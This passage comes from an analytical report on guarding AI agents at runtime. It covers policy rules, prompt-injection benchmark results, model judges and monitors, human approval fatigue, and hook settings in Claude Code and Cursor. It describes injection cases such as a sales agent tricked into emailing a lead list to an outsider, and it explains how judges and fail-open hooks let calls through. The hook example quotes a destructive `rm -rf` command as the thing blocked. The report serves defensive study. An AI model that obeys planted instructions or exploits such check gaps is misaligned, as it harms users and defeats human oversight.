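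A wrong argument name in a rule is harder to notice than a deadlock. An email rule in the same study looked for an argument called `recipient`, but the email tool called it `recipients`, so the rule loaded normally and never blocked anything. On the office tasks, where most of the rules had this kind of fault, attacks succeeded 7.7% of the time, compared with 7.3% with no protection at all. A log would not reveal the fault, because a rule that never matches looks the same as a rule that nobody has broken. Simply comparing the rule with the tool's list of arguments reveals it.

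Other rules run but don't match the policy they came from. NOMOS turned a clause telling agents to check that a bill was overdue before requesting payment into a ban on requesting payment *while* a bill was overdue. Yu and colleagues caught this by replaying the rule over recordings of the agent working without it. The rule would have blocked 47 of the 49 payment requests in runs that had ended successfully. Companies could run the same test on their own logs before switching a rule on, although a successful run can still include a call that the policy forbids.

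The rule about basic economy bookings contained a subtler error. It blocked every use of the tool that updates flights, but that tool also changes the cabin, which the airline's policy allows if customers keep their flights. Yu and colleagues had made the same mistake in the rules they wrote by hand as an independent standard, so comparing the two sets could not reveal it. A second model found the error by checking the conversations against the full policy.

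Handwritten rules have other errors. When Reddy and colleagues audited their four checks, the cancellation check had been right all 161 times it blocked a call, while another had been right only 5% of the time. An average over the four would have hidden this difference.

Finally, a policy requirement may have no rule. NOMOS extracted rules from 6 of the 8 sections of the airline policy and 8 of the 12 sections of the retail policy. Of the 40 violations that still got through in retail, 21 fell under two clauses for which NOMOS had produced no rule. Palumbo and colleagues check translations in both directions, looking for requirements that have no rule and rules that match no requirement, but they don't guarantee that a translation is correct.

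### Attacks stopped and work lost

Most tests of these systems against attackers use AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates banking, Slack, travel booking and office work. Each test gives the agent a user's task and hides an attacker's instruction in something the agent will read. The benchmark then scores whether the agent completed the user's task and whether the attack succeeded. AgentDyn is a harder benchmark of the same type, in which the user's task often requires the agent to follow instructions from third parties.

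The table gives the rates without and with each check. The last column covers runs with no attack, so the drop there comes mostly from the check preventing legitimate work.

| Study | Test | Agent's model | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Palumbo and colleagues | AgentDojo, all four areas | GPT-4o | 25.2% → 1.7% | 79.0% → 57.3% |
| Zhang and colleagues | AgentDojo, all four areas | DeepSeek-v4-pro | 6.1% → 0.0% | 87.8% → 75.5% |
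| Zhang and colleagues | AgentDyn | DeepSeek-v4-pro | 8.6% → 0.7% | 76.7% → 60.0% |
| Yu and colleagues | AgentDojo, banking | gemma-4-26B | 46.5% → 0.0% | 79.2% → 70.8% |
| Yu and colleagues | AgentDojo, travel | gemma-4-26B | 10.0% → 3.6% | 75.0% → 70.0% |
| Yu and colleagues | AgentDojo, office work | gemma-4-26B | 7.3% → 0.0% | 87.5% → 65.0% |
| Yu and colleagues | AgentDojo, Slack | gemma-4-26B | 70.5% → 0.0% | 90.5% → 14.3% |

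All three systems stopped nearly every attack that needed a tool call, and most of the attacks that still succeeded didn't need one. In four of the five successful travel attacks, the attacker only wanted the agent to recommend a particular place, which gives a check on tool calls nothing to block. The size of the improvement depends as much on how vulnerable the agent was to begin with as on the check. Only 3% to 7% of the AgentDojo attacks succeeded against Zhang and colleagues' four models when undefended, so a reduction to zero is less impressive there than on Slack.

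The amount of lost work varies much more, from 5 points in travel to 76 on Slack. Yu and colleagues trace most of it to whether the user names the target of an action. Their provenance rules allow only targets the user has named and, in banking, known payees. Banking customers usually name the person they want to pay. On Slack, a typical honest task is to summarise an article a colleague posted and send the summary to the team, so the agent has to act on a link it found by reading. An injected link reaches the agent the same way, and the rules block both.

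The sales agent would do about as badly as Slack under such a rule, since it gets every enquirer's address by reading the form. It can do its job only if the rule also accepts the contact field, which means trusting text a stranger typed. Yu and colleagues leave open whether a system can accept such targets without letting the attacks back in.

Finer rules let the agent complete more tasks than strict ones. Palumbo and colleagues compared two policies in FORGE. Under both, the agent also received a reminder of the user's request after each batch of tool results. A strict policy refused any consequential call once untrusted content had entered the context, and the agent completed 33.2% of tasks. With a policy that checked where each argument came from, it completed 62.5%. Attacks succeeded less than 1% of the time under both. With the reminder alone, 14.1% of attacks succeeded and the agent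 completed 83.7% of tasks, so even the finer policy reduced the number of completed tasks by about a quarter. In another of AgentDojo's defences, a model chooses in advance which tools a task needs. When this was combined with the reminder, 3.1% of attacks succeeded and the agent completed 73.4% of tasks, which some companies might prefer.

Rules also work poorly on tools and tasks they weren't developed for. When Zhang and colleagues applied rules developed on AgentDojo to AgentDyn, no attack succeeded, but the agent completed only 10% of its tasks, compared with 60% under rules developed for AgentDyn. The good results in the table come from rules made for the tools and types of task they were tested on, and people had also reviewed the AgentDyn rules. With a fully automatic process and less training data, the best of three models produced rules that allowed 53% of tasks, and the other two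 produced rules that allowed about 30%.

These studies give weak evidence about which system is best, because each team tested its rivals' software itself. In Zhang and colleagues' AgentDyn tests, an agent under CaMeL, which separates trusted from untrusted data, completed no tasks. Yu and colleagues quote CaMeL's headline result as 77% of tasks completed, against 84% without it. The benchmarks and models differ, and the teams may not have taken equal care with somebody else's system. Corners has published the rules for NOMOS, which Yu and colleagues print in full, but has kept the code private. AgentDojo has no written policies, so Yu and colleagues wrote their own. For Slack, travel and office work, they also designed some of the available conditions with the tests in mind.

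### Mistakes when nobody is attacking

Fixed rules can also help an agent complete ordinary tasks. In τ²-bench, the airline's tools carry out any well-formed request, even one that the company's policy forbids. Reddy and colleagues found that 78% of the failures they saw left the database wrong without any error message. Their four checks raised the share of tasks that GPT-4o mini completed from 29.6% to 42.0%, and a repeat with three times as many trials gave almost the same gain. Nearly all of the gain came from the cancellation check. The newer GPT-5.2 improved from 61.2% to 71.6%, but the researchers ran that test only once.

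Other teams also saw gains on the airline tasks. Under FORGE, the average score for three models (Claude Opus 4.5, GPT-5.2 and Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview) rose from 74.7% to 81.5%, although Gemini's score fell slightly. Under NOMOS, gemma-4-26B rose from 39.2% to 47.6%. That difference could be chance on single attempts, but it was clearer when Yu and colleagues required the agent to succeed two, three or four times in a row.

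Scores barely changed on the retail tasks, where FORGE's average rose by about one point and NOMOS's fell by two. Reddy and colleagues argue convincingly that this is because the retail tools already reject many forbidden requests, so the agent gets an error and can correct its mistake. A company that can build such rules into its tools may not need a separate check for them.

Yu and colleagues also counted policy violations separately from the score. In retail, the score stayed flat, but the share of the agent's changes that broke the policy fell from 30.8% to 6.9% under the rules. For the airline, it fell from 66.3% to 2.6%. Most of the original violations were changes that the customer had not confirmed, and the count depends on how strictly one reads the policy. If a single "yes" can cover several announced changes, the airline's starting figure drops to 36.8%. The airline agent also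 made fewer changes under the check, 116 instead of 353, because the check blocked many of its attempts.

Palumbo and colleagues tested an approval rule on a group of agents that look up drug side effects. Each agent was supposed to get a supervisor's approval before reading the official drug labels, and approval for one session did not carry over to the next. The agents made 40 unapproved lookups in 15 trials with only written instructions, and none with FORGE. When FORGE blocked them, the agents read the error message, requested approval and tried again. They reached the right answer every time in both conditions.

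### Delay

The decision takes almost no time compared with a call to a language model, which typically takes seconds. NOMOS needed about 3 microseconds per decision on average. FORGE has to query its graph, and with 32 agents running at once, the median wait measured from the agent's side was 0.72 milliseconds.

Refusals add more delay, because the model has to read the error and propose something else. On AgentDojo, FORGE raised the median running time by about 6% but the mean by 30%, from 5.93 to 7.70 seconds. A minority of runs must therefore have taken much longer, probably those in which the agent kept retrying. Zhang and colleagues' results do not cover delay. ActGov would probably be slower than the others, since a model has to extract some of the facts before the rules can run.

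### Attackers who know the rules

A benchmark's attacks are fixed in advance, while a real attacker can study a defence and adjust. Among these studies, only Yu and colleagues' describes a test with attacks that adapt to the defence. The main tests by Palumbo and colleagues and by Zhang and colleagues used the benchmarks' own attacks, and Reddy and colleagues studied an agent's mistakes with no attacker involved.

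Yu and colleagues extended the banking attack with false claims meant to get past their rules, such as that the account holder had approved the payment or that the payee was already known. These attacks succeeded 34.7% of the time without the check and in none of 144 cases with it, although the agent tried to make the attacker's call in 61 of those cases. The claims did not affect the check because NOMOS takes facts only from tool results and the user's own messages, not from the agent's assertions.

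However, the same team wrote both the attack and the defence, and the attack consisted only of statements in text. The team did not try to plant a false record in the transaction history, which the rules treat as accurate, and AgentDojo's attacks cannot create such records.

The score of zero also leaves out some harm. In 7 of the 144 cases, the agent sent an injected payment to somebody already in the account's history. The attacker gained nothing, so the benchmark counted the attack as a failure, but the user had not asked for the payment. In one run with the benchmark's standard attack, Llama-3.3-70B sent $40,000 to a known payee in four payments, although the user had only asked a question. The rules allowed each payment because the payee was in the history.

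## Judging uncertain calls with a model or a person

Fixed rules can't settle every call. For instance, they can't determine whether the sales agent's reply answers the question or gives away something the enquirer shouldn't have. The check can allow all such calls, block them all, or pass them to a second language model (usually called a judge) or a member of staff to read and decide.

### What a model judge reads

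The software at the enforcement point sends the judge a description of the proposed call and instructions for assessing it. *AgentTrust* (2026) reproduces one such prompt in full. The prompt has slots for the type of action, the tool's name, a description, the content, the parameters and any further context. The judge rates five kinds of risk, including data exposure and how hard the action would be to reverse. It returns a verdict (allow, warn, block or review), a confidence between 0 and 1, and a short reason, all in a fixed format that ordinary code can process.

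If the judge reads everything the agent has read, an instruction planted in a web form reaches the judge too. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, tries to prevent this in its auto mode, where a judge replaces most approval prompts. Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026) announced a preview of the mode in March 2026, and the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026) says interactive sessions on every plan now start in it by default. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that the judge sees only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. The software removes the results of earlier calls, because planted instructions arrive in them, and the agent's own prose, so the agent can't argue for its call.

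In the sales example, such a judge would receive a request for a summary, followed by an email of the whole lead list to an outside address. It could detect that nobody had asked for this email without reading the form. A legitimate reply is harder to judge because, without the results of `read_leads`, the judge can't determine whether an unfamiliar address came from the form. Anthropic accepts this loss of provenance to keep injected text away from the judge.

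Anthropic also varied how much the judge saw. Adding the agent's prose and the tool results made the judge worse at catching overeager actions, in which an agent tries to help but goes beyond what the user authorised. When the judge saw only the tool calls, it missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked things that users had plainly asked for.

When one agent delegates work to another, the first agent's instruction reaches the second agent's judge as if a user had written it, so everything looks authorised. Claude Code therefore also runs the judge at the moment of delegation, when the user's original request is still visible.

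### From a score to a decision

A judge's score has no effect until code compares it with a threshold. *Think Before You Act* (2026) describes an example of this in JevAct, a decision gate. Before deployment, a language model turns a company's policy into yes/no questions for each tool that changes records. It also writes a rule for combining the answers, and ordinary code to check facts that are in the records, such as dates and amounts. For the airline tasks in τ²-bench, the model wrote 86 questions, including one about whether the user requested a cancellation or only enquired about it.

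While the agent runs, a model called Kev reads the conversation and the proposed call and gives a probability for each answer. Code then applies the threshold:

```
P(yes) ≤ 0.05  →  the answer counts as "no"
P(yes) > 0.05  →  the answer counts as "yes"
```

Suppose Kev estimates a 3% probability that the user requested the cancellation. That counts as a "no", and if the rule requires a "yes", the agent gets the call back with an explanation. An estimate of 20% counts as a "yes", so the cancellation can go ahead even though, by Kev's estimate, the user probably didn't request it. This low threshold avoids needless interruptions. A company more worried about theft could set it at 50%, but would then block more legitimate calls.

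After sending a proposed change back twice, JevAct also lets the next proposal run unchecked. This stops a mistaken judge from blocking an agent forever, but a hijacked agent could get past the check by repeatedly proposing changes. JevAct is meant to make agents more reliable, and its tests involved no attackers.

In those tests, the clearest gains came on τ²-bench's telecom tasks, where the agent helps a customer fix a phone and JevAct checks that the agent isn't giving up too early. The share of tasks solved in all three attempts rose for all eight agents, by an average of 16.9 percentage points. On the airline tasks, it rose for four agents and fell for two. On BFCL, a benchmark of tool calling with no written policy, it rose for all nine agents, by between 0.1 and 9.6 points.

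The judge's own contribution is less certain. In a single run of the 50 airline tasks, GPT-4.1 completed 50% without the gate, 57.1% with the judge's questions alone, 68% with the code checks alone and 72% with both. It therefore completed two more tasks with both than with the code checks alone. With another agent, gpt-oss-120b, flagging calls at random helped as much as the full gate, so the benefit apparently came from making the agent try again. The telecom gain also disappeared when a different model played the customer.

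Among 101 incorrect calls in a labelled sample, 42 failed none of the questions, because the questions came from the company's policy and did not cover what the user had requested. This matters for security because a judge can only check a call against the questions it is given. Kev costs about a sixth of a cent per airline task, compared with 1.3 to 2.3 cents for the commercial language models tested in the same role.

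### How often judges are right

A judge could do well in many tests by learning that refunds are usually allowed and deletions usually aren't. *Same Operation, Different Permission* (Jing, Chen and colleagues, 2026) removes this shortcut by keeping the operation the same and changing only the evidence of permission. For example, a refund is allowed while a delegation is active and forbidden after someone revokes the delegation. Two of the eight judges gave the right answer in all 160 test cases, half of which were forbidden. Another, based on Nvidia's Nemotron, allowed 58 of the 80 forbidden operations. Qwen3Guard, which looks for harmful content, allowed 72. Content filters are unsuited to checking permission because a forbidden refund contains nothing offensive.

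The team then tested models on 1,215 requests written for two conventional permission engines. Qwen3.5-27B got 99.1% right, with one wrong approval and ten wrong refusals. The engines supplied the correct answers, so a company that already keeps its permissions in this form gains nothing by asking a model. The result is more encouraging for companies whose permissions exist only in prose, although the examples were public and the models may have seen them in training.

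A second judge did not reliably help. When Jing and colleagues required approval from both Qwen3.5-27B and a model called Safeguard, the pair avoided the one wrong approval but refused 171 more legitimate requests. Adding Qwen3.5-27B to the much weaker Qwen3.5-9B was worthwhile because it removed 260 of 261 wrong approvals and only eight correct ones.

Some apparent successes also came from broken output. In one run, Qwen3.5-9B had to give its findings and evidence in a structured answer, and no forbidden operation got through. But 58 of the 80 blocks happened because the software couldn't read the answer, and only 22 were real refusals. The same fault blocked legitimate work, so only 10 of the 80 permitted operations ran. Forcing the output into a valid format raised that number to 71 and still let no forbidden operation through.

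Judges are harder to assess when the agent already resists most attacks. Shaw (2026), in *Silent Failures in Agentic Security Evaluation*, tested a judge on the calls of GPT-5.6 Terra. Only one of 43 attacks succeeded without any defence. The judge did not improve on this, and the share of harmless tasks that failed rose to 11.5%. Shaw cautions that 43 attacks are too few to show a small benefit.

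*Ajar* (Sharma, Lin and colleagues, 2026) avoided this problem by testing defences on calls the agent never made. It presented each defence with calls that ordinary AgentDojo tasks did not need, giving more weight to irreversible actions and to those affecting money or other people. By this measure, Claude Code's auto mode allowed 30% of the unneeded calls. A plain list of the tools each task required, with no limits on their arguments, allowed 36%. Permission Assistant, which also uses a model to judge each call, allowed only 8%, but it reduced the share of completed tasks by 11.3 points, against 3.4 for auto mode. The test is somewhat harsh on auto mode, which is meant to stop destructive or outward-facing actions rather than every unnecessary one. It also presented each call to auto mode without the calls that would normally precede it.

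Anthropic's own figures show what moving a threshold does. Auto mode's judge first gives a quick yes or no, with instructions to block when in doubt. If it flags a call, it looks again and reasons at length. Anthropic tried this on 10,000 real calls by its employees' agents and on 52 real overeager actions:

| | Harmless calls blocked | Overeager actions missed |
|---|---|---|
| Quick answer only | 8.5% | 6.6% |
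| Quick answer, then reasoning | 0.4% | 17% |

The second look removed most of the false alarms but let more of the dangerous actions through. Because there were only 52 cases, the true miss rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the judge had identified the danger but wrongly treated it as something the user had agreed to. A user who says "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) has not agreed to overwriting the project's shared history.

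Later tests were more favourable, though Anthropic paid for or ran them. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that none of 720 prompt injection attempts succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. This is weak evidence about the judge, since attacks succeeded only 0.09% of the time against Anthropic's latest models without it. The same evaluation gives better evidence about OpenAI's Codex, where turning on a comparable review mode cut the success rate of attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol from 19.03% to 5.83%. OpenAI has since released a new version of that mode.

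### False alarms when attacks are rare

Even an accurate judge produces mostly false alarms if nearly every call is harmless. Suppose, for illustration, that a company's agents make 100,000 calls, 10 of them malicious, and that the judge catches 95% of malicious calls and wrongly blocks 1% of harmless ones. It would block about 1,000 harmless calls and nine or ten malicious ones.

```
True blocks:   10 × 0.95      =  9.5
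False blocks:  99,990 × 0.01  ≈  1,000
Share of blocks that are right:  9.5 / 1,009.4  ≈  0.9%
```

The judge stops nine or ten attacks and about a thousand pieces of honest work. Changing one assumption at a time shows which improvements matter:

| Change | True blocks | False blocks | Share of blocks that are right |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 9.5 | 1,000 | 0.9% |
| Judge catches every attack | 10 | 1,000 | 1.0% |
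| False alarms fall to 0.4% | 9.5 | 400 | 2.3% |
| Fixed rules settle 90,000 harmless calls first | 9.5 | 100 | 8.7% |

Better detection barely improves the ratio of wrong blocks to right ones, which would be about 40 to 1 even at Anthropic's false-alarm rate of 0.4%. The largest gain comes from not sending obviously harmless calls to the judge. Claude Code skips the judge for read-only tools and for edits inside the user's project.

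False alarms also add up within a task. If an agent makes 20 judged calls and each has an independent 1% chance of being wrongly blocked, about 18% of tasks will have at least one wrong block. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (2026) measured a similar effect in detectors that look for injected instructions in tool results. One detector, ProtectAI v2, flagged 30.1% of harmless results on AgentDojo, which would have stopped 69.1% of tasks. It had flagged only about 1% of ordinary emails, so a company can't judge a detector by its false-alarm rate on ordinary text. False-alarm rates on harmless tool results ranged from zero to over 90% across detectors.

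How much a false alarm disrupts the agent's work depends on what happens next. Claude Code tells the agent why the judge refused and lets it look for another way, so many false alarms lead only to a retry. After three refusals in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code asks the user. If no user is available, the process ends.

### The dispute over intent and action

Capsule Security, which found ShareLeak and PipeLeak, sells a judge of this kind that uses fine-tuned small language models to assess every tool call before it runs. Its chief executive, Naor Paz, said in the VentureBeat article reposted on diyhaven858.wasmer.app that "intent is the new perimeter." Capsule argues that attackers can spread an attack over several harmless-looking messages, so only a judge that follows the whole conversation will notice it.

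CrowdStrike's Elia Zaitsev disagrees. He told VentureBeat that "intent analysis cannot always work" because it can give different answers to the same question. He considers observing actions a solvable problem, and CrowdStrike's software tracks which programs an agent starts and what they do. Both companies sell the approach they recommend, and VentureBeat's article gives no detection rates for either product.

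Zaitsev is right that judges are inconsistent. When Sharma and colleagues repeated their test with identical input, auto mode gave the same verdict about 95% of the time and Permission Assistant about 92% to 93%. In one repeat, auto mode allowed 80 calls that it had correctly refused before. An attacker whose agent can keep trying might eventually get a call allowed, so a limit on refusals is useful. Verdicts varied by a similar amount in systems where a model writes a policy and ordinary code enforces it, because the model wrote a somewhat different policy each time. But a company can write such a policy once, review it and keep it, which it can't do with a judge's future verdicts.

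An honest reply and a leak can both be calls to `send_email`, so observing the action isn't enough to tell them apart. A person or a model has to interpret the email's text in light of the request. The action is stronger evidence when it is suspicious in itself, such as when a coding agent searches a computer for passwords that its task doesn't need.

Other critics say, as the O'Reilly article did, that a model judge has the same weakness it is supposed to guard against. How serious this is depends on what the judge reads. A judge that reads the whole context can be misled by the same planted sentence as the agent. Auto mode's judge never sees the web form, so an instruction there has to influence the agent first and then produce a call that still looks acceptable. The attacker's words can still reach the judge if the agent copies them into an email body or a shell command. Fixed rules also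 have critics. Carter Rees, an AI executive at the company Reputation, told VentureBeat that defences built on them are insufficient for agents.

The measurements support using a judge as an extra check but not as the only one. Auto mode caught most of the real overeager actions, including kinds that would be hard to describe in advance, but it missed roughly one in six.

### What a person sees and how often they approve

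The alternative is to ask a person. In Claude Code's manual mode, the agent pauses and shows the user the command it wants to run, and the user approves or refuses it. How useful this is depends on what the prompt contains. If the sales agent's prompt showed only an outside address and the subject "Leads", the theft would look like any other reply. To catch it, an employee would need to see and read the body of the email, the enquiry it answers and where the address came from.

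Anthropic found that users accepted 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts, and its later figure, from August 2026, was 97%. These rates aren't proof that users are careless, because most commands are safe. In the example with ten malicious calls in 100,000, a perfect reviewer would still approve 99.99% of calls.

Better evidence comes from an experiment that Anthropic ran with 1,053 paid testers. Each tester approved or refused commands while working on coding tasks, and the software replaced one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused it 13.6% of the time, while auto mode's judge blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers' refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

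Anthropic had a product to promote, and the testers worked in an artificial environment with nothing of their own at risk, so developers might take more care with their own code. But a quarter of Claude Code's interactive sessions started with permission checks switched off, which is consistent with the experiment's result. Anthropic also reports that, among sessions its safety systems had flagged, serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested was more common under manual approval (6.3%) than in auto mode (2.4%). This is weaker evidence, because users chose their own mode and a model graded the harm.

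These results weaken the case for sending every call the judge flags to a person. In the illustrative example, a reviewer would receive about 1,010 flagged calls, nine or ten of them malicious. If the reviewer did only as well as Anthropic's testers, they would refuse one or two of the malicious calls and approve the other malicious ones, leaving the company less safe than if it had blocked every flagged call. A security analyst who knew that each call was suspicious would probably do better, but would still spend most of the time on false alarms.

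### Which calls to send to a person

Human attention is limited, so it makes sense to reserve it for calls where a mistake would be serious. One starting point is Sharma and colleagues' harm scale, which rates actions by whether they can be undone and whether they affect only the user or also money and other people. A reversible change to the user's own files is near the bottom, and an irreversible payment to a stranger is at the top. Anthropic likewise still recommends that a person review high-stakes changes to production systems (the ones a business runs on).

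The scale is too coarse for the sales agent. Nobody can unsend an email, and every reply goes to an outsider, so every reply would need approval. The company could instead require a person's approval only for replies that break one of its narrower rules about recipients and contact details.

Asking people to approve a whole plan at once could reduce the number of prompts. Claude Code's users rejected 39% of plans, compared with 3% of individual permission requests, so they seem to read plans. But they may often reject a plan because they want the work done differently, so the higher rate is weak evidence that they can spot an attack. An employee who approves a plan before the agent reads the web form also can't see what a planted instruction will later make the agent do.

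When Salesforce recommended human approval after PipeLeak, Paz replied in VentureBeat's article, "If the human should approve every single operation, it's not really an agent." He sells an alternative to human approval, but the evidence of fatigue supports his objection to approving *every* operation. Salesforce eventually adopted a narrower rule that requires confirmation only for emails, so an agent that mostly updates records would seldom have to stop. But if an agent spends the day answering enquiries, the employee would have to approve nearly everything it does, and after 50 routine replies might well approve an email containing the lead list too.

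## Vendor hooks in coding agents

Claude Code and Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, let customers attach their own checks through hooks. Both agents edit files and run commands, often on a developer's own computer.

According to Anthropic's *Hooks reference*, a Claude Code hook can run a script, call a webhook, use a tool on an MCP server, prompt a language model, or start a second agent that inspects files before it answers. A hook can therefore apply either fixed rules or a model's judgment.

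### One blocked command in Claude Code

Anthropic illustrates the mechanism with a script that stops the agent from deleting whole folders. The customer registers it in a settings file with four pieces of information, simplified here:

```
event:      PreToolUse     (before a tool call runs)
matcher:    Bash           (only calls to the shell tool)
condition:  Bash(rm *)     (only commands that delete files)
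script:     block-rm.sh    (the customer's check)
```

Suppose the model proposes the command `rm -rf /tmp/build`, which deletes a folder and everything in it.

1. The event fires, and Claude Code holds the call.
2. Claude Code compares the tool's name with the matcher. Both are `Bash`, so it goes on.
3. It compares the command with the condition. A command such as `npm test` would fail here, and the script would never start.
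4. The script receives the call as JSON, a text format for structured data, and searches the command for `rm -rf`.
5. The script finds it and prints a decision. Claude Code blocks the call and gives the model the reason, so the model can try something else.

The main part of what the script receives looks like this:

```json
{ "tool_name": "Bash",
  "tool_input": { "command": "rm -rf /tmp/build" } }
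```

And this is the decision it prints:

```json
{ "hookSpecificOutput": {
    "hookEventName": "PreToolUse",
    "permissionDecision": "deny",
    "permissionDecisionReason": "Destructive command blocked by hook" } }
```

The condition in step 3 is fairly thorough. Claude Code splits a compound command into its parts and tests each one, and if it can't determine what a command will run, it starts the script anyway. Anthropic still calls this filter best-effort and recommends Claude Code's own permission rules for a firm ban. The example script is cruder, since it looks for one piece of text and doesn't block a deletion written differently.

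The script also receives the location of the conversation's transcript, but Claude Code writes the transcript with a delay, so the latest messages may be missing when the hook runs. This makes the transcript an unreliable source for a rule that depends on earlier calls, such as "no upload after reading a password file". To enforce such a rule, a customer could instead add a second hook that runs after each successful call and records it in a separate log.

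Hooks can change a call as well as block it. Anthropic's *Intercept and control agent behavior with hooks* includes an example that redirects every new file into a separate folder. In auto mode, a hook may alter a call after the judge has reviewed it, so Claude Code can refuse the altered call, though it makes exceptions for some scripts that alter shell commands or file edits.

### What a silent hook means

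If the command had been `rm file.txt`, the example script would have found no `rm -rf` and exited without printing anything. The hook would have made no decision, so the call would still go through the normal permission rules, which may allow it, block it or require the developer's approval.

A hook that prints "allow" usually makes Claude Code skip asking the developer for approval. But if a permission rule in the settings file blocks the call or requires approval, that rule still applies.

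When several hooks return decisions on the same call, the strictest one applies. From most to least strict, the decisions are "deny", "defer" (which pauses an unattended run until another program supplies an answer), "ask" and "allow". A hook can therefore add a refusal but cannot cancel another hook's. However, if a company's security hook returns no decision and a developer's convenience hook returns "allow", the developer may not see an approval prompt that would otherwise have appeared.

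### Who controls the hook

Developers can define hooks for a single project or for all their projects. They can store a project's hooks in its repository, so everyone who works on the code gets them. Plugins and skills, which are add-ons for the agent, can include their own hooks. Administrators can define hooks for the whole organisation in managed settings.

Claude Code merges all of these. Developers can add their own hooks but can't remove the administrator's. The setting that turns off all hooks leaves the administrator's running unless an administrator sets it.

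A repository's hook scripts run with all of the developer's permissions on the computer. In an interactive session, Claude Code doesn't run hooks until the developer agrees to trust the folder. In an unattended run, nobody is there to agree, so Claude Code treats the folder as trusted and runs any hooks the repository contains. Anthropic advises reading an unfamiliar repository's settings files before such a run, or turning hooks off for it.

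An administrator can go further with the `allowManagedHooksOnly` setting, which blocks hooks from users, projects and plugins, except plugins the administrator has made compulsory. This stops a stranger's script or a developer's careless "allow", but it also blocks hooks that developers wrote for good reasons, including ones stricter than the company's. Despite the setting's name, SDK hooks still load, according to *Claude managed-settings.json · Codex requirements.toml*, a configuration guide from the security company PromptArmor. Applications register these hooks through the Agent SDK, Anthropic's kit for building other software on Claude Code.

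Managed hooks protect only the sessions they reach. Anthropic's *Deploy managed settings* describes three main ways for an administrator to deliver them, and ranks them in this order:

1. Remote settings, which Claude Code fetches from Anthropic's web console or from a gateway the company runs.
2. A policy that the company's device-management software installs on each computer.
3. A settings file in a system folder.

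By default, Claude Code uses the highest-priority source that contains any policy and ignores nearly everything in the others, without a warning. Suppose a security team puts its hook in the settings file on every laptop. If a colleague then sets a default model in the web console, Claude Code stops running the hook. The `/status` command shows which source is in use, and since version 2.1.242 an administrator can tell Claude Code to merge the sources.

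Delivering hooks remotely also adds a delay. Claude Code checks the console hourly, and in an interactive session a new or changed hook takes effect only after the developer accepts it in a dialog.

Where the agent runs also affects how it can receive hooks. A cloud session on Anthropic's computers can't read a file on the developer's laptop, so its hooks have to come from the console. Cowork, an Anthropic product that runs on Claude Code, never fetches policy from the console, and when it runs remotely it has no laptop policy to read either. A company that uses all three needs to deliver its hook at least twice and still won't reach remote Cowork sessions. The hook therefore meets Anderson's first requirement on some of the company's computers but not on others.

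### Failures that let a call through

When a script ends, it returns a number called an exit code to the program that started it. By convention, 0 means success and any other number means some kind of failure. Claude Code treats three cases differently:

- With exit code 0, the hook has worked. Claude Code follows any decision it printed, and otherwise applies the normal permission rules.
- With exit code 2, Claude Code blocks the call, even if the script also printed "allow".
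- With any other code, Claude Code follows a valid printed decision if there is one. Without one, it treats the hook as broken and carries on.

The third case is easy to get wrong because 1 is the usual failure code, and many programmers would use it to refuse a call. Anthropic warns that a hook that exits with code 1 and prints no decision does not block the call.

By default, and with an exception on Windows, each of these failures lets a call proceed:

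- The script is missing or can't start.
- The script crashes, or ends with a code other than 0 or 2 and no valid decision.
- The script ends with code 0 but prints JSON that Claude Code can't read.
- A script, webhook or MCP tool exceeds its time limit, which is ten minutes unless the customer changes it.
- A webhook can't connect, returns an error status, or returns something other than JSON.
- An MCP tool reports an error, or its server isn't connected.

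Webhooks have a problem similar to the one with exit code 1. A web service normally refuses a request with an error status such as 403 ("forbidden"), but Claude Code treats that as a broken hook and lets the call continue. To block the call, the service has to return a *success* status with "deny" in the body. If an administrator restricts which addresses webhooks may use, the allowed addresses must include the company's own service, because the restriction also applies to managed hooks.

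When a hook times out, the call proceeds to the normal permission rules, so a developer in manual mode may still be asked to approve it before it runs. But if the developer has switched permission checks off, the hook may be the main safeguard.

Customers can reverse the default for scripts and webhooks by setting `onFailure` to `"block"`, which makes Claude Code block the call whenever the hook fails. With this setting, a script that prints "allow" but ends with an unexpected exit code also counts as a failure. Anthropic suggests testing the setting by leaving the script out and asking the agent to list a folder. If the setting is on, Claude Code blocks even this harmless command.

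The setting requires version 2.1.295 or later. Administrators can stop older versions from starting, but sessions already open keep running. MCP tool hooks have no such setting. The setting also has no effect on hooks that run in the background, because Claude Code doesn't wait for their response.

The default already blocks the call in two situations. One is on a Windows computer without Git Bash, a program that supplies a Unix-style command line. If a script that runs before a tool call fails on such a computer, the failure can block the call. If the developer later installs Git for Windows, the same settings may let calls through, so one laptop can block a call that another with an identical policy allows. Anthropic recommends setting `onFailure` explicitly.

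The other is a callback, a function inside an application built with the Agent SDK. If a callback times out before a tool call, Claude Code blocks the call and reports to the model that the hook gave no answer. Anthropic explains a similar choice for callbacks that screen users' prompts by saying that such a callback may be enforcing a policy, so an unscreened prompt should not get through. The argument applies just as well to a script that screens shell commands. Scripts probably have the looser default because many only format code or write logs, and developers would not want a broken formatter to stop their work.

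### How Cursor differs

Cursor made much the same choice. According to Cursor's *Hooks*, a script that exits with code 2 blocks the action, for compatibility with Claude Code. After any other failure code, the action goes ahead. If a customer sets `failClosed` to true on a hook, a crash, a timeout or invalid JSON also blocks the action. Cursor recommends this setting for security-critical hooks on MCP tools.

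Cursor has one general event, `preToolUse`, that fires before every kind of tool, and narrower events for shell commands, MCP tools and file reads. Hooks on the shell and MCP events can return "ask" to have a person confirm the action. The format for `preToolUse` also accepts "ask", but Cursor doesn't currently enforce it there, so a company that wants a person to confirm certain file edits can't rely on it.

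Cursor ranks hooks by who installed them: enterprise first, then team, project and user. All matching hooks run, and if their decisions conflict, the higher-ranked source takes precedence. This gives administrators firmer control, but as worded, the rule could let a permissive enterprise hook's "allow" override a project hook's "deny", whereas in Claude Code the denial would stand.

Administrators on Cursor's enterprise plan can write team hooks in a web dashboard, and Cursor copies them to every member's computer about every half hour. They can also use device-management software to place hook files on each machine.

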